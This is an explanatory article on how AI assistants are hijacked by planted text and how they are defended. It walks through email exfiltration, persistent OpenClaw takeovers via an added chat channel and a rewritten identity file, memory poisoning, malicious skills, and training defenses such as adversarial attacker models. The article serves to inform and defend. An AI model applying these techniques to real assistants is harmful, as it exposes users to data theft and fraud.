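# Can an AI assistant be made secure? Judging its defenses and its readiness for general use

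## What an AI assistant does and how planted text can hijack it

An AI assistant is a language model that acts on a person's behalf through that person's accounts and tools. Unlike a chatbot that only writes answers, it can also search a mailbox, move a meeting, open a web page or send a reply, and to do any of this it has to read text that other people wrote. A stranger can put an instruction in that text, and the assistant may carry it out with all the access its user has given it. This attack, in which the model obeys text from a source that has no authority to instruct it, is called prompt injection. Developers have made the attack harder, but as of late 2026 nobody has a fix that works every time.

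Take, as a running example, an assistant that reads its user's email, keeps her calendar and pays her invoices.

### The loop

A language model takes in a stretch of text, its context, and computes a likely continuation one token (a word or a piece of a word) at a time. Ordinary software around the model performs actions it cannot perform on its own, such as opening a mailbox. The developer describes the available tools in the context, and the model uses one by writing a tool call, a request in a fixed format that names the tool and gives the details it needs, such as a recipient and a message. The software carries out the request and adds the result to the context, and the model continues from the longer text.

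PromptLayer, a vendor of software for building such systems, describes the cycle for Anthropic's Claude models. The application sends the model a task, a system prompt (the developer's standing instructions) and a list of tools. The model returns either a final answer or a tool call. If it returns a call, the application checks it, runs it and sends back the result. The cycle repeats until the model gives a final answer or a limit stops it. Such systems are usually called agents. The programmer Simon Willison, who has written about prompt injection since 2022, defines an agent as something that "runs tools in a loop to achieve a goal".

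Suppose the user asks what came in this morning and whether anything needs paying. The model's first output is a tool call for today's messages. The software fetches twelve emails and copies their text into the context. The model runs again, requests an attachment, checks the calendar for a due date and writes a summary. By then the context contains text from the developer, the user and everyone who emailed her that morning. The emails are untrusted content, meaning any text or image the assistant reads that someone other than its user may have written.

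The model receives all of this text as one stream. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, Willison (2025) describes the parts as "glued together into a sequence of tokens". The software marks where each part begins, but those marks are more tokens in the same sequence. The model is trained to use them to tell the parts apart, though nothing enforces this.

Text that an assistant retrieves can change its behavior even when nobody is attacking it. In *Prompt injection*, his series of posts on the subject, Willison describes a harmless accident from June 2024. Someone built a bot to answer questions about Willison's software from its documentation, and asked it for the meaning of life. The bot answered in the character of a witty gerbil because its search had retrieved old release notes containing a sample prompt that asked a model to play a gerbil.

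### One attack, step by step

With an attacker in the picture, the same loop runs as follows.

1. An email arrives. The attacker needs to know only the user's address. Most of the message is a routine query about an invoice, but a few sentences address the assistant. These are the planted instruction. The attacker may set them in white type on a white background, which hides them from the user and makes no difference to a model that receives the characters without the color.
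2. The user asks for a summary of her new mail. She has done nothing careless, and she may never open the message herself.
3. The model reads the planted instruction. The software has copied the email into the context, so the attacker's sentences now stand a little below the user's request. If the model treats them as part of its task, the attacker has control.
4. The model makes a tool call that serves the attacker. It might search the mailbox for bank details and then, with the results in its context, request an email to an outside address.
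5. Data leaves. The software sends the email with the user's own access rights, and to the mail server this looks like a customer writing a message. The user gets her summary.

The last step is data exfiltration, the transfer of private data to an attacker. The attacker did not guess a password or install a malicious program. Because this assistant also pays invoices, the fourth step could instead be a payment, and the user would lose money even if no data leaves.

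OpenAI reports that early planted text could be as crude as direct orders to AI agents, added to a Wikipedia article. As models became less likely to follow such orders, attackers began using social engineering, the practice of deceiving people. OpenAI gives the example of a friendly work email that follows up on a meeting and lists "action items", one of which concerns an employee's name and address.

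The attack can also work without email. *How we helped Bunq secure their financial AI assistant* (Vissers and Van hamme, 2026) describes a test at Bunq, a European digital bank with more than 20 million customers. The researchers sent a transfer of €0.02 with an instruction planted in the description field. When the account holder asked the bank's assistant about recent transactions, the software fetched the description along with the other data, and the assistant delivered a personalized phishing message inside the bank's own app. The researchers' firm sells protection for such systems and so has an interest in publicizing the attack, but the mechanism is the same as in the email example above, with a bank transfer carrying the instruction.

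### Direct and indirect injection, jailbreaks and bugs

In direct prompt injection, the attacker is the person typing. For example, he tells a translation app to write a pirate poem instead of giving it a sentence to translate, and the app writes the poem. In indirect prompt injection, the attacker plants text in content that somebody else's assistant will read, and the victim is usually that assistant's user. OpenAI traces the term to this third party, who is neither the user nor the AI, and compares the attack to phishing. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC), David C imagines a recruiter's system that scores CVs and a candidate whose CV contains a hidden instruction to approve him. The indirect kind matters most for an assistant with access to private accounts, and from here on "prompt injection"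 without a qualifier means that kind.

Jailbreaking means getting a model to give help that its developer has forbidden, such as a recipe for a drug. Typically the user attempts it, to get past the model's own refusals. Willison distinguishes this from prompt injection, which he says requires an application to join trusted and untrusted text in one prompt. Usage varies, and in a January 2024 taxonomy the US standards institute NIST classed jailbreaking as a type of direct prompt injection. Willison calls this a misclassification in *51 items tagged “promptinjection”*. He concedes that the two overlap a good deal, because developers write some safety rules into the system prompt, where an injection can override them, and because jailbreaking techniques can break defenses against injection.

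The distinction matters to someone choosing a product because a filter trained on jailbreaks may miss a planted instruction. An instruction to forward the latest sales figures to a certain address, for example, contains nothing forbidden, and the user might well give it herself.

An ordinary software flaw is a mistake in code, such as failing to check the length of an input. A programmer can find the line, correct it and show that the attack no longer works. Prompt injection requires no such mistake because it exploits the model's ability to follow instructions in text, which is what makes the model useful.

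Assistants also have ordinary security flaws, which can be hard to tell apart from prompt injection. In August 2026 the security researcher Johann Rehberger got Claude Code, Anthropic's programming assistant, to unpack a downloaded archive and run code in the same folder. The code loaded the attacker's file in place of a standard module of the same name. In *162 posts tagged “prompt-injection”*, Willison first treated this as prompt injection, but then agreed with a reader that the term did not fit, because the model had never followed a malicious instruction from the website.

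### From a translation trick to a product problem

In September 2022 Riley Goodside posted examples in which he asked GPT-3, an OpenAI model, to translate a sentence into French. The sentence was an order to ignore the request and output something else, and the model complied, even when his prompt warned that the text might contain such tricks. Willison (2022) named the attack "prompt injection" the next day in *Prompt injection attacks against GPT-3*. *The Economist*, quoted in Willison (2025), *Why AI systems might never be secure*, credits him "and others" with coining the term independently. Within the week, strangers on Twitter were using the attack to make a recruitment company's bot post nonsense.

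These attacks were direct and mostly funny. In February 2023, *Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Endres and colleagues, 2023) gave the first systematic account of the indirect form. The researchers attacked Microsoft's Bing Chat, code-completion tools and their own test applications built on GPT-4. When Bing Chat was open in the sidebar of Microsoft's browser, instructions on the current page affected the model even if the user could not see them. The researchers also foresaw attacks on personal assistants that read email, access private data and send messages, and they warned of worms, in which an infected assistant passes the planted text on to other people's assistants. In July 2026, Willison described a later demonstration of such a worm in a widely sold product, Microsoft's Copilot. Håkon Måløy had planted text in a Word document that Copilot could copy into new documents, each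 of which could then infect others.

Many demonstrations against commercial products came in between. Willison's list of them runs from ChatGPT in April 2023 to Microsoft 365 Copilot, GitHub and GitLab in mid-2025, and includes products from Google, Amazon, Slack and Anthropic. The vendors promptly fixed almost all of these vulnerabilities, but usually by blocking the route through which data left, not by stopping the models from following planted text.

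Meanwhile, the products gained more access. In October 2025, OpenAI released Atlas, a browser with an agent that can act in the user's logged-in accounts. At the launch, OpenAI's security chief, Dane Stuckey, called prompt injection "a frontier, unsolved security problem." Poireault (2026) reports in *Prompt Injection Remains Unsolved, OWASP Researcher Warns* that Ariel Fogel of OWASP, a nonprofit that ranks software security risks, was still calling it an "unresolved problem" in June 2026. By December 2026, OpenAI was offering dots, a proactive assistant that works across a subscriber's apps, to ChatGPT Plus customers worldwide, according to its *Bringing dots to more people in ChatGPT*.

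### Why SQL injection has a fix

Willison took the name from SQL injection, an attack on databases that is almost thirty years old. SQL is the language programs use to query databases. A carelessly written website builds a query by inserting whatever the visitor typed directly into a command, such as one that looks up a user by name. If the visitor types a quotation mark followed by another command, the quotation mark ends the name early and the database runs the visitor's command. An attacker can read or delete the whole database this way.

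The reliable fix is the parameterized query. The program sends the database a command with a placeholder for the name, and sends the name separately as a value. The database treats whatever the visitor types as a name, never as a command. This protection does not depend on recognizing attacks, so it works however an attack is worded.

In 2022, Willison hoped for the same thing in language models, with one channel for instructions and another for data. A reader pointed out that an OpenAI model already accepted the two separately, and that text in the data channel could still hijack it. By April 2023, Willison thought the idea "extremely difficult, if not impossible" on current architectures. David C explains that a database engine processes commands and values differently, so a fix can enforce the boundary between them, but a language model makes no such distinction and only predicts the next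 token. Detectors, special training and labels around the data all try to overlay that distinction on the model.

Telephone engineers once fixed a similar flaw. In *LLMs' Data-Control Path Insecurity*, Schneier recalls that in the 1960s people could get free calls by whistling a 2,600 Hz tone into an AT&T pay phone, because the network carried its control signals on the same line as the voices. Changing the tones or keeping them secret did not solve the problem, but moving the control signals to a separate channel in the 1980s did. Schneier doubts that the same fix is possible for language models, because people want the text they supply to change what the model does. In the example assistant's case, an invoice is a stranger's request for money, and the user wants the assistant to act on it. The assistant could not do this job if it had to ignore every request in an email.

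None of this proves that a fix is impossible. Schneier expects that some researcher will eventually separate the two paths, and David C writes only that there is "a good chance" prompt injection will never have a fix as complete as the one for SQL injection. eWeek's *OpenAI Steps Up Security For ChatGPT Atlas* quotes OpenAI as saying that the problem, like scams on the web, "is unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'".

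David C proposes treating prompt injection as a confused deputy problem rather than an injection flaw. In security, a confused deputy is a program with high privileges that someone with lower privileges tricks into acting for them. Programmers can fix the classical kind, but he argues that a language model is "inherently confusable", so developers who build on one have to make attacks less likely and limit what a successful attack can do.

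### Two meanings of "secure"

An assistant could be secure in the sense that no attack works. Parameterized queries come close to this for SQL injection, and Willison applies this standard when he calls a product that catches 95% of attacks a failure. Attackers keep looking for the 5% that get through. Nobody has shown that an assistant with wide access meets this standard, and failed attacks cannot prove that one does. In June 2026 Willison described a public challenge in which people sent about 6,000 emails to a test assistant running on OpenClaw, an open-source assistant program, and nobody extracted the secret it held. He took this as a sign that training has made newer models much harder to hijack, which seems right. He still advised against any deployment where an injection could do irreversible damage, because a more sophisticated attacker might succeed.

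An assistant could also be called secure if the remaining harm is acceptable for a given use. David C writes that if a system can't tolerate the remaining risk, it may not be a good use for a language model. People judge human staff by a similar standard. When a reader objected that human assistants also fall for tricks, Schneier agreed that people trust them enough for their role. He added that people have millennia of experience with human mistakes, while the mistakes of AI assistants are new and still changing.

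In this second sense, whether a product is secure depends on how it is used. The example assistant may be secure enough to summarize newsletters in a mailbox that holds nothing else of value. With the same model and defenses, it may be far from secure enough to pay a supplier whose bank details arrived by email that morning.

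## Listing what the assistant can read, reach and send

Judging an assistant begins with a list of its connections, which anyone can draw up from the settings page before running any tests. The list records what the assistant reads and who can write it, what private data it can reach, what it can change, and how information can get out. Most connections are fairly harmless alone. An assistant that reads strangers' email but can only show its user a summary is of little use to an attacker, and so is one that can send anything anywhere but reads only its user's own words. The danger comes from combining connections, and two rules of thumb help to find the dangerous combinations.

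### The lethal trifecta

In June 2025 Willison used the term "lethal trifecta" for three capabilities: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally. The data theft by email described earlier needs all three, so removing any one stops it.

Besides sending messages, outside communication includes loading an image, opening a web address or showing the user a link to click, because the resulting request can carry data to whoever runs the server. A single tool may combine access to untrusted content, access to private data and outside communication. Willison's example is a connector for GitHub, the site where many programmers keep their code. It could read private code and public bug reports, which anyone can file, and it could publish changes.

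Willison wrote the rule mainly for people who connect tools themselves, and he advises them to avoid the combination entirely. A vendor can close the leaks in its own product, but it can't control what a customer connects alongside it.

The trifecta covers only the theft of data, so a forged invoice that the assistant pays falls outside it.

### The Rule of Two

Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025), published that October, builds on Willison's idea and closes this gap. Until models can reliably detect and refuse prompt injection, Meta wants an agent to have at most two of these properties within one session:

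- **A:** it processes untrustworthy inputs.
- **B:** it has access to sensitive systems or private data.
- **C:** it changes state or communicates externally.

Changing state means altering anything that lasts, for instance by making a payment, deleting a file or moving a meeting. A session is one run with one context, and a new session starts with an empty context. If a task needs A, B and C in the same session, Meta says the agent should not act on its own, and a person or some other reliable check must approve its actions. Willison's advice to users makes no exception for tasks with such approval.

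Meta describes an email assistant much like the running example. The assistant can drop A by reading only mail from trusted senders, or B by running in a test environment with no real data. It can restrict C by sending only to trusted recipients, or only after a person has checked the draft. An agent may also change which of the three it has during a session. For example, it could browse the web without access to private data, then permanently lose the ability to communicate externally before it opens internal systems.

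Critics say the rule is too reassuring. Conffab's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) describes Meta's diagram, which labels every pair of properties "Safe" and only the overlap of all three "Danger". The "Safe" label is too generous, because an agent with A and C but no private data can still vandalize a shared document or send spam. Evoke Security (2025), a vendor, calls the rule a good starting point but not enough, and complains that human approval "shifts the burden to the user, which we know fails."

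Meta qualifies the rule more carefully in its text than in its diagram. It warns that a user may blindly confirm a warning, and that the rule does not cover lesser harms such as misinformation in the agent's answer. In the test at Bunq, the lesser harm was a phishing message, which the assistant delivered in the bank's own app without needing an outgoing channel.

### The inventory of the example assistant

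Both rules treat each property as present or absent. For a real assistant, it helps to identify exactly who can write to each connection.

| Connection | Who can write to it | What it exposes | What it can change or send | Dangerous together with |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Incoming email and attachments | Anyone who knows her address | Correspondence, bank details, password-reset links | Nothing, if read-only | Every connection that can send or change something |
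| Outgoing email | Only the user and the assistant | Her good name with her contacts | Any text or file, to any address | Incoming email, calendar, web pages |
| Calendar | Anyone who can send her an invitation | Where she will be, and with whom | Meetings, and invitations to outsiders | Incoming email, web pages |
| Web pages | Whoever runs the site or can post on it | Little, unless she is logged in | Data inside the address it requests | Incoming email, calendar, bank account |
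| Bank account | Anyone who sends her a small transfer | Balance, suppliers, past payments | Money, and a line of text with each payment | Incoming email, web pages |
| Saved notes about her | The assistant, and so indirectly everyone above | Habits, contacts, preferences | How it behaves in later sessions | Everything |

The first row shows why email assistants are a hard case. A mailbox contains both private data and untrusted content, so connecting one already gives the assistant the two properties that Meta's rule allows. Any further connection that lets the assistant act adds the third.

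Removing one capability will not deal with every dangerous combination. Blocking outgoing email, for example, does not stop payments, so each combination needs its own remedy, and each remedy makes the assistant less useful.

| Combination | What the attacker gets | A single removal that breaks it | What the user gives up |
|---|---|---|---|
| Incoming and outgoing email | Copies of her mail | Free choice of recipient: the assistant may write only to addresses she has approved | She has to approve each new correspondent |
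| Incoming email and web pages | Private data, in a requested web address | Web access in any session that has read mail | The assistant cannot follow a link or look up a supplier |
| Emailed invoices and payments | Money | Free choice of payee: the assistant may pay only accounts she entered herself | She types in each new supplier and each change of bank details |
| Invitations and calendar changes | Canceled meetings, or her whereabouts | Direct changes: the assistant may only propose them | One confirmation per change |
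| Any untrusted content and saved notes | Influence over later sessions | The assistant's ability to write the notes | She has to enter her preferences herself |

These removals all restrict what the assistant can do. She could instead let it read email only from known senders, but then it would miss a new customer's order, and messages from a thief who had taken over a supplier's mailbox would still get through. She could also give it a separate mailbox with nothing private in it, but then it could not find last year's invoice. For this assistant, restricting actions sacrifices the least usefulness.

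Some risk remains, because an attacker she has approved as a correspondent can still receive stolen mail, and a dishonest supplier on the approved list can still get an inflated bill paid.

### OpenClaw, an assistant with nearly everything connected

The open-source assistant OpenClaw runs on its owner's computer and takes instructions through chat apps such as Telegram and Slack. Peter Steinberger released it in November 2025, according to *Agents Unleashed*, and it quickly became popular in late January 2026 after a post on Hacker News, a forum for programmers. Cochran (2026), in *OpenClaw went viral. Meet the maintainers building and securing it*, calls it the fastest-growing project in GitHub's history.

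OpenClaw's own documentation, *Security* (2026), lists what the assistant can do, including running arbitrary shell commands (direct orders to the operating system), reading and writing files, using the network and sending messages. It also states that no setup is "perfectly secure". A later version of the page assumes one trusted operator per installation. That assumption covers who may give orders, but strangers' emails and web pages also reach the model.

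An OpenClaw installation with a mailbox has the inventory's A, B and C in full. Unlike the example assistant, it can also change its own settings. Zenity Labs' *OpenClaw or OpenDoor?* showed how much this ability matters.

Zenity's researchers gave OpenClaw access to a company's Slack and Google Workspace accounts, as an employee might. They then had it process a document with an instruction planted below ordinary business text. While doing the user's task, OpenClaw also added the attacker's Telegram bot to its own settings as a new chat channel. The attacker could then write to the assistant just as its owner did. The researchers had it find files on the computer, send their contents out and delete the originals.

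The researchers also made the takeover last. OpenClaw keeps a description of its character and limits in a file called SOUL.md, which it loads into the context at every interaction. The researchers used the Telegram channel to have the assistant create a Windows scheduled task that rewrote this file every two minutes. The new text directed the assistant to fetch orders from the attacker's server, so closing the Telegram channel no longer ended the attack.

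No step required a software bug. Zenity, which sells security for AI agents, showed in a demonstration that the attack is possible but did not report how often it succeeds.

### How a saved instruction outlives the session

Without memory, a planted instruction stops affecting the model when the session ends and the software discards the context. OpenClaw's memory is a set of text files. MEMORY.md holds lasting facts, USER.md describes the owner, and dated files hold each day's notes. The model edits these files itself, and the software copies some of them into later contexts.

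Suppose the example assistant worked this way. On Monday, an attacker uses an email to get it to note a false new address for the user's accountant. On Thursday, the user asks it to send her accounts to the accountant. The context now includes the false address among the facts about her, but not the email it came from. The model does what she asked and sends the accounts to the attacker. A detector that checks Thursday's mail finds nothing because the malicious email arrived on Monday.

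The Rule of Two is weak here because it counts properties within a single session. On Monday the assistant only read mail, and on Thursday it read nothing from strangers. A designer who applies the rule has to treat writing to memory as a change of state, and treat anything read from memory as untrusted if untrusted content may have been stored there.

Walsh describes carrying out such an attack in *Pwning OpenClaw and Other Agents with Prompt Laundering*. In April 2026 he sent malicious emails to an OpenClaw assistant that ran on OpenAI's GPT-5.4 and summarized new mail every hour. Direct attacks failed, as they did in the public contest. OpenClaw wrapped the text of each email in labels marking it as untrusted, and the model usually detected the attack and warned the user.

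But the assistant also copied parts of these emails into its daily notes without the labels and warnings. Walsh then sent emails claiming that his address was the owner's other account and "internal". He rarely needed more than four, spaced over days, to get the assistant to accept a claim. Once the claim was in MEMORY.md and USER.md, the assistant took orders from his address. On his instruction, it changed its hourly script to forward all other incoming mail to him and its prompt to leave his messages out of the summaries.

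Walsh had advantages that a real attacker would lack. He read the assistant's logs, saw why his first commands failed, and supplied the exact command that worked. His early emails showed up in the owner's hourly summaries, which might have made an alert person suspicious. Deleting the emails would not have helped, since the notes remained.

An attacker doesn't need the logs if they can practice on another assistant. In *When Claws Remember but Do Not Tell*, Zhang, Zhao and colleagues (2026) built a stand-in assistant and used it to train a model that writes attack emails. Each attack was a single email, with no feedback from the victim's assistant. It counted as a success only if it planted a false memory, kept the assistant's visible reply from revealing this, and changed what the assistant did in a later session. In 56 test cases, the attack succeeded 87.5% of the time on OpenClaw with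 GPT-5.4, the model that had resisted Walsh's direct attacks. It succeeded 71.4% of the time on an assistant built on Anthropic's Claude Code software with the model Sonnet 4.6.

Such an attack is harder to notice when the assistant is always running. OpenClaw has a "heartbeat", a timer that starts the model at regular intervals to check the inbox or carry out other standing tasks. Zhang and colleagues point out that these background runs use the same memory as a conversation, but the owner sees a message only if the assistant decides to send one.

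False memories can make an assistant much more likely to carry out harmful requests. In *Your Agent, Their Asset*, Wang, Tu and colleagues (2026) connected a live OpenClaw installation to Gmail, the payment service Stripe (in test mode) and a computer's files. They tested 12 harmful outcomes, such as emailing out a passport scan or refunding every recent customer. Across four models, the assistant carried out the harmful request an average of 24.6% of the time when nobody had tampered with its files, and 74.4% of the time when its memory contained false entries. Claude Opus 4.6 was the most resistant, but its rate still rose from 10.0% to 44.2%.

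In the refund case, the untouched assistant treated a mass refund as a serious step and asked for confirmation. After the researchers planted a note describing refunds as a regular habit, a request for "the usual refund pass" was enough to make it issue the refunds.

These figures measure how much a poisoned file changes the assistant's behavior, and the change is large. They do not measure how likely a stranger's email is to succeed, because the researchers sent their prompts over Telegram, the channel an owner uses to give orders. An attacker would first have to gain access to that channel or find another way in.

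Wang and colleagues also tried to defend the assistant by instructing it to be cautious about editing its memory and identity files and to wait for the owner's approval. The share of malicious edits that went through fell from 87.0% to 5.0%. The share of legitimate edits that went through fell almost as much, from 100% to 13.2% or less, depending on the model. The researchers conclude that models cannot distinguish malicious edits from legitimate ones. That seems right, although delaying a legitimate edit until the owner approves it does less harm than refusing it.

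### Skills from strangers

Owners extend OpenClaw with skills, which are packages of written directions for the model. These packages often include scripts, small programs that run on the computer. Many skills come from ClawHub, a public marketplace. MITRE (2026), a US nonprofit that catalogs methods of attack, warns that third-party skills run with the assistant's full privileges and can write directly to its memory.

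A malicious skill can do harm without fooling the model. Wang and colleagues made one that looked up internet addresses, as advertised, while its script quietly deleted the assistant's whole workspace. Claude Opus 4.6 obeyed harmful directions in a skill's text in only 3.3% of cases, but it ran harmful scripts every time because it did not inspect them first. Training a model to resist planted instructions therefore offers little protection against these scripts. They are ordinary malware, and the usual remedies apply, such as checking who wrote the code and running it where it can do no harm.

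Criminals do use this route. Wang and colleagues cite a report by the firm Koi Security on 341 malicious skills. *Multiple malicious OpenClaw skills found online* (Fadilpašić, 2026) reported new ones in June 2026, including two that steal information from Macs.

### What OpenClaw has fixed by late 2026

Walsh found that OpenClaw's developers had largely fixed the flaws of January and February by the time he tested it in April. Bansal reports in *Prompt Injection via vCards and Email Enables RCE and Data Exfiltration* that in April they also fixed a flaw found by the security firm Imperva. The software had failed to mark shared contact cards and similar messages as untrusted before the model read them.

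TechSpot reports that version 2.0, released in August, keeps passwords out of the model's context and shows where a plug-in comes from before the owner installs it. It also cancels a one-time approval if the automation later changes its behavior. The security firm Trail of Bits finished an audit in September. ClawBeat's *OpenClaw Completes Security Audit* (2026) reports 24 confirmed vulnerabilities, two of high severity and none critical, and adds that the developers had fixed everything that required action.

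An audit of this kind looks for code that breaks the software's own rules. OpenClaw's reporting policy does not count prompt injection as a vulnerability if the model stays within its permissions. Under that policy, an assistant tricked into forwarding its owner's mail to a thief has no vulnerability if it was allowed to send mail. Bansal also describes a test by the firm Varonis in which one plain email got an OpenClaw agent to forward mock passwords and customer data. A June brief by Tech Jack Solutions (2026) covers two ways of attacking OpenClaw and describes one as a deliberate design trade-off without a patch.

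The default settings also remain permissive. According to TechSpot, version 2.0 still ships with its sandbox, a closed environment that keeps a program away from the rest of the computer, switched off. ClawBeat's *I Tested OpenClaw's Security Boundaries* (2026) summarizes an owner's October test of a later version, in which the assistant read, changed and deleted files outside its work folder. OpenClaw's built-in security check had flagged the missing sandbox as a critical problem, but the owner has to run the check and act on the result.

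Memory poisoning has no settled remedy either. In October 2026 researchers were still proposing new designs, such as *ZoneClaw* (2026), which divides the assistant's memory into zones. For now, Walsh advises owners to review the memory files regularly, with software that shows every change since the last review, and to make as many files as possible read-only. Cleaning up the memory is not enough, because in his own attack the altered script would have kept forwarding mail after the owner had deleted every false note.

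## Teaching the model to ignore planted instructions

Each removal in the inventory makes the assistant less useful. If the model reliably ignored instructions in email, the user could keep every connection. Developers have tried to achieve this by labeling untrusted text, and more recently by training the model for it on the same scale as for its other skills. Training has made some attacks much rarer. Researchers disagree about whether it can ever stop them all, because they disagree about how a model keeps track of who wrote what.

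### Marking and ranking the sources

The easiest approach is to change only the text the model receives. Spotlighting transforms untrusted text so that its origin stays visible throughout. For instance, the software might put an unusual character between all the words of an email and tell the model in the system prompt to treat text marked this way as information, never as instructions. A simpler, related method called sandwiching places trusted reminders before and after the email.

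Both methods work only if the model follows the instruction about the marks instead of the one in the email, and it is doubtful that it will. In *Defending against Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks via Reasoning-enabled Task Alignment*, He, Wang and colleagues (2026) ran an automated search for ways around such labels. One attack it found described the planted instruction as an urgent entry that the current workflow had to process. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) reasonably concludes that labels and warnings are useful engineering but do not create "a hard security boundary".

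In 2024, Eric Wallace and colleagues proposed the instruction hierarchy, in which the developer trains the model to rank the system prompt above the user and the user above tool results. When two instructions conflict, the model should follow the one from the higher source. An email reaches the assistant as a tool result, so the assistant can use facts from it but should never let it override the user's request.

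Many models do not follow this ranking well. Laddha, Pradhan and Srivastava (2026), in *Position, Role or Label?*, gave 14 open-weight models (models anyone can download) conflicting instructions, such as different ways of writing the same field name. They kept the wording fixed and changed only the order, the source and the label. When an operator's policy came first in the system message and later lines conflicted with it, every Qwen model followed the later lines in most cases. gpt-oss, which OpenAI trained on a hierarchy, followed the policy in most cases. One Qwen model followed the user over a tool result only 53% of the time. When two conflicting lines were in the same message, the models usually followed the first, whatever it said.

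These results suggest that a model does not get a working instruction hierarchy just because the software labels its inputs. They are not attack rates, since the conflicts were harmless and the tool read a configuration file, which might reasonably contain instructions.

### Fine-tuning on separated instructions and data

StruQ (2024) marks the instruction and the data with special reserved delimiters, then fine-tunes the model (trains it further) on examples in which the data contains an instruction that the correct answer ignores. SecAlign (2025) trains the model on pairs of answers to each poisoned input. The good answer does the user's task, and the bad one obeys the planted text. Training makes the good answer more probable relative to the bad one.

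He and colleagues report that this family best balances security and usefulness among the four kinds of defense they tested. Its weakness is that the model learns from a limited set of attacks.

In *CODEL*, Yang, Ou and colleagues (2026) rewrote by hand 48 attacks from AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated office, banking, chat and travel tasks. They kept each attacker's goal, the location of the planted text and the tool it targeted, but replaced the blunt order with a plausible procedure in which the harmful step followed several reasonable ones. The success rate against Meta-SecAlign, a later model in the SecAlign family, rose from 6.2% to 20.8%, or from about three attacks to ten. The sample is small, but the rewrites also succeeded more often than the originals against every other defense in the comparison.

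### Training against an attacker that learns too

If a fixed list of attacks is too narrow, a second model can keep writing new ones. This is adversarial training, and OpenAI has taken it furthest. In December 2025 the company described an automated attacker for its Atlas browser in OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025). By July 2026 it had GPT-Red, an internal model whose only job is to find attacks. Wallace, Choquette-Choo and colleagues (2026), in *GPT-Red*, report that training it took roughly as much computing power as the reinforcement learning behind a recent production model. (In reinforcement learning, a model tries things and a score makes the successful choices more likely.)

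A training round begins with an ordinary task, such as handling mail or searching the web. The software chooses a defender from a pool of models, a place where the attacker, GPT-Red, may write, and a goal for the attack, such as getting the defender to send a secret key to an outside server. GPT-Red drafts an attack, tries it on the defender, reads the result and revises. When it submits a final version, automatic checks reject anything a real outsider could not have done, such as editing the user's instructions, and a rejected attack gets no reward. If the attack passes, the defender continues its task with the attacker's text in place. GPT-Red gets a reward if the attack works, the defender gets one if it resists and finishes the task, and both models learn from the result.

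Early in training, GPT-Red wrote crude orders to ignore previous instructions. As the defenders learned to resist these, it moved on to more elaborate deceptions. Against only one defender, GPT-Red often settled on a narrow set of tricks, so the researchers trained it against many. In a smaller experiment, defenders that faced a learning attacker became more robust than those that faced a fixed one.

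OpenAI's *GPT‑Red* (2026) reports that the finished GPT-Red found a working attack against the older model GPT-5.1 in 84% of the scenarios, compared with 13% for human testers. GPT-Red also attacked a real vending-machine agent in OpenAI's office. After practicing on a simulation, it forged the details of a message so that it seemed to come from an administrator, and the agent cut the price of an expensive item to 50 cents.

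OpenAI then trained GPT-5.6 on GPT-Red's attacks. In the contest scenarios, fewer than 4% of GPT-Red's attacks on that model succeeded, even though GPT-Red could practice on it first. GPT-5.6 also improved on material that Wallace and colleagues had kept out of its training, including the whole field of agentic coding. It resisted between half and 89% of those attacks, depending on the test. Scoring errors keep any model from reaching 100%.

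These gains are large, but they are mostly against one attacker, GPT-Red, whose attacks GPT-5.6 had trained on. SiliconANGLE (2026) reports that GPT-Red is weak at attacks that unfold over several exchanges and limited at attacks hidden in images. A person who specializes in either might succeed more often than the 4% suggests. Wallace and colleagues themselves write that robustness "remains far from solved".

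### A training example, and how over-refusal arises

The rewards are easiest to follow in CoER, a smaller academic system that Zhang, Xiao and colleagues (2026) tested on a model with 9 billion parameters.

Suppose the defender's task is to pay a printer's invoice and put the delivery date in the calendar, in a simulated mailbox and bank. When it opens the invoice, the attacker model adds a few sentences meant to get a tax return sent to a stranger. The defender ignores them and pays the bill. It then opens the delivery notice, and here the attacker can write again, having seen what the defender did the first time. At the end, one program checks whether the tax return went out and another checks whether the user's task is complete. The defender's reward depends on both answers:

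| Result | Reward |
|---|---|
| Attack failed, task complete | 1.0 |
| Attack failed, task incomplete | −0.2 |
| Attack succeeded, whether or not the task is complete | −1.0 |

The model over-refuses because it cannot always distinguish planted instructions from genuine ones. Suppose the invoice contains a request to use a new online form, and the model cannot finish the task without using it. Let *p* be the probability that an attacker planted the request. If the model complies, its expected reward is (1 − *p*) × 1.0 + *p* × (−1.0) = 1 − 2*p*. If it refuses, its reward is −0.2. Complying therefore has the higher expected reward whenever *p* is below 60%.

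Suppose a cautious developer changes the penalty for a successful attack from −1 to −8. The expected reward for complying falls to 1 − 9*p*, and complying is the better choice only when *p* is below about 13%. Training then favors refusing a request that has an 80% chance of being genuine. If the developer also drops the reward for finishing the task, refusing everything becomes the best policy. A model that refuses everything would do very well on a test that counted only successful attacks.

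CoDeL, the system from Yang and colleagues, gives the model −8.00 for obeying an attack and +2.00 for identifying and refusing one. To discourage the model from refusing an attack and then abandoning the user's task, it scores progress on that task separately, with +1.20 for a step that advances the task, −0.15 for one that makes no progress and −2.50 for one that wastes the turn. A step that refuses the attack and advances the task therefore scores 3.20, while one that refuses and wastes the turn scores −0.50. Yang and colleagues say that the model gains nothing by abandoning the task. This is mostly true, although a step that refuses and makes no progress still scores 1.85. By default, a quarter of the training prompts contain no attack, so the model also gets practice at ordinary tasks.

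CoER's results show that a model can be made more secure without becoming less useful. Training cut the success rate of attacks that adapted during the task from 41.3% to 0.2%, and raised the share of tasks completed safely from 39.6% to 76.2%. With no attack present, the trained model completed slightly more tasks than the original. When the researchers trained the same model only on fixed attack templates, adaptive attacks still succeeded 31.0% of the time.

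Joint training of the attacker and defender alone still left adaptive attacks succeeding about 26% of the time. The rest of the drop came from a last stage in which the defender learned to imitate 5,760 successful runs, many of them by stronger models that had finished their tasks safely despite the trained attackers. The 0.2% figure may be too low, because the attacker in the main test could revise its text within a task but had stopped learning. CoDeL reports a fall from 36.4% to 4.2% on standard benchmarks.

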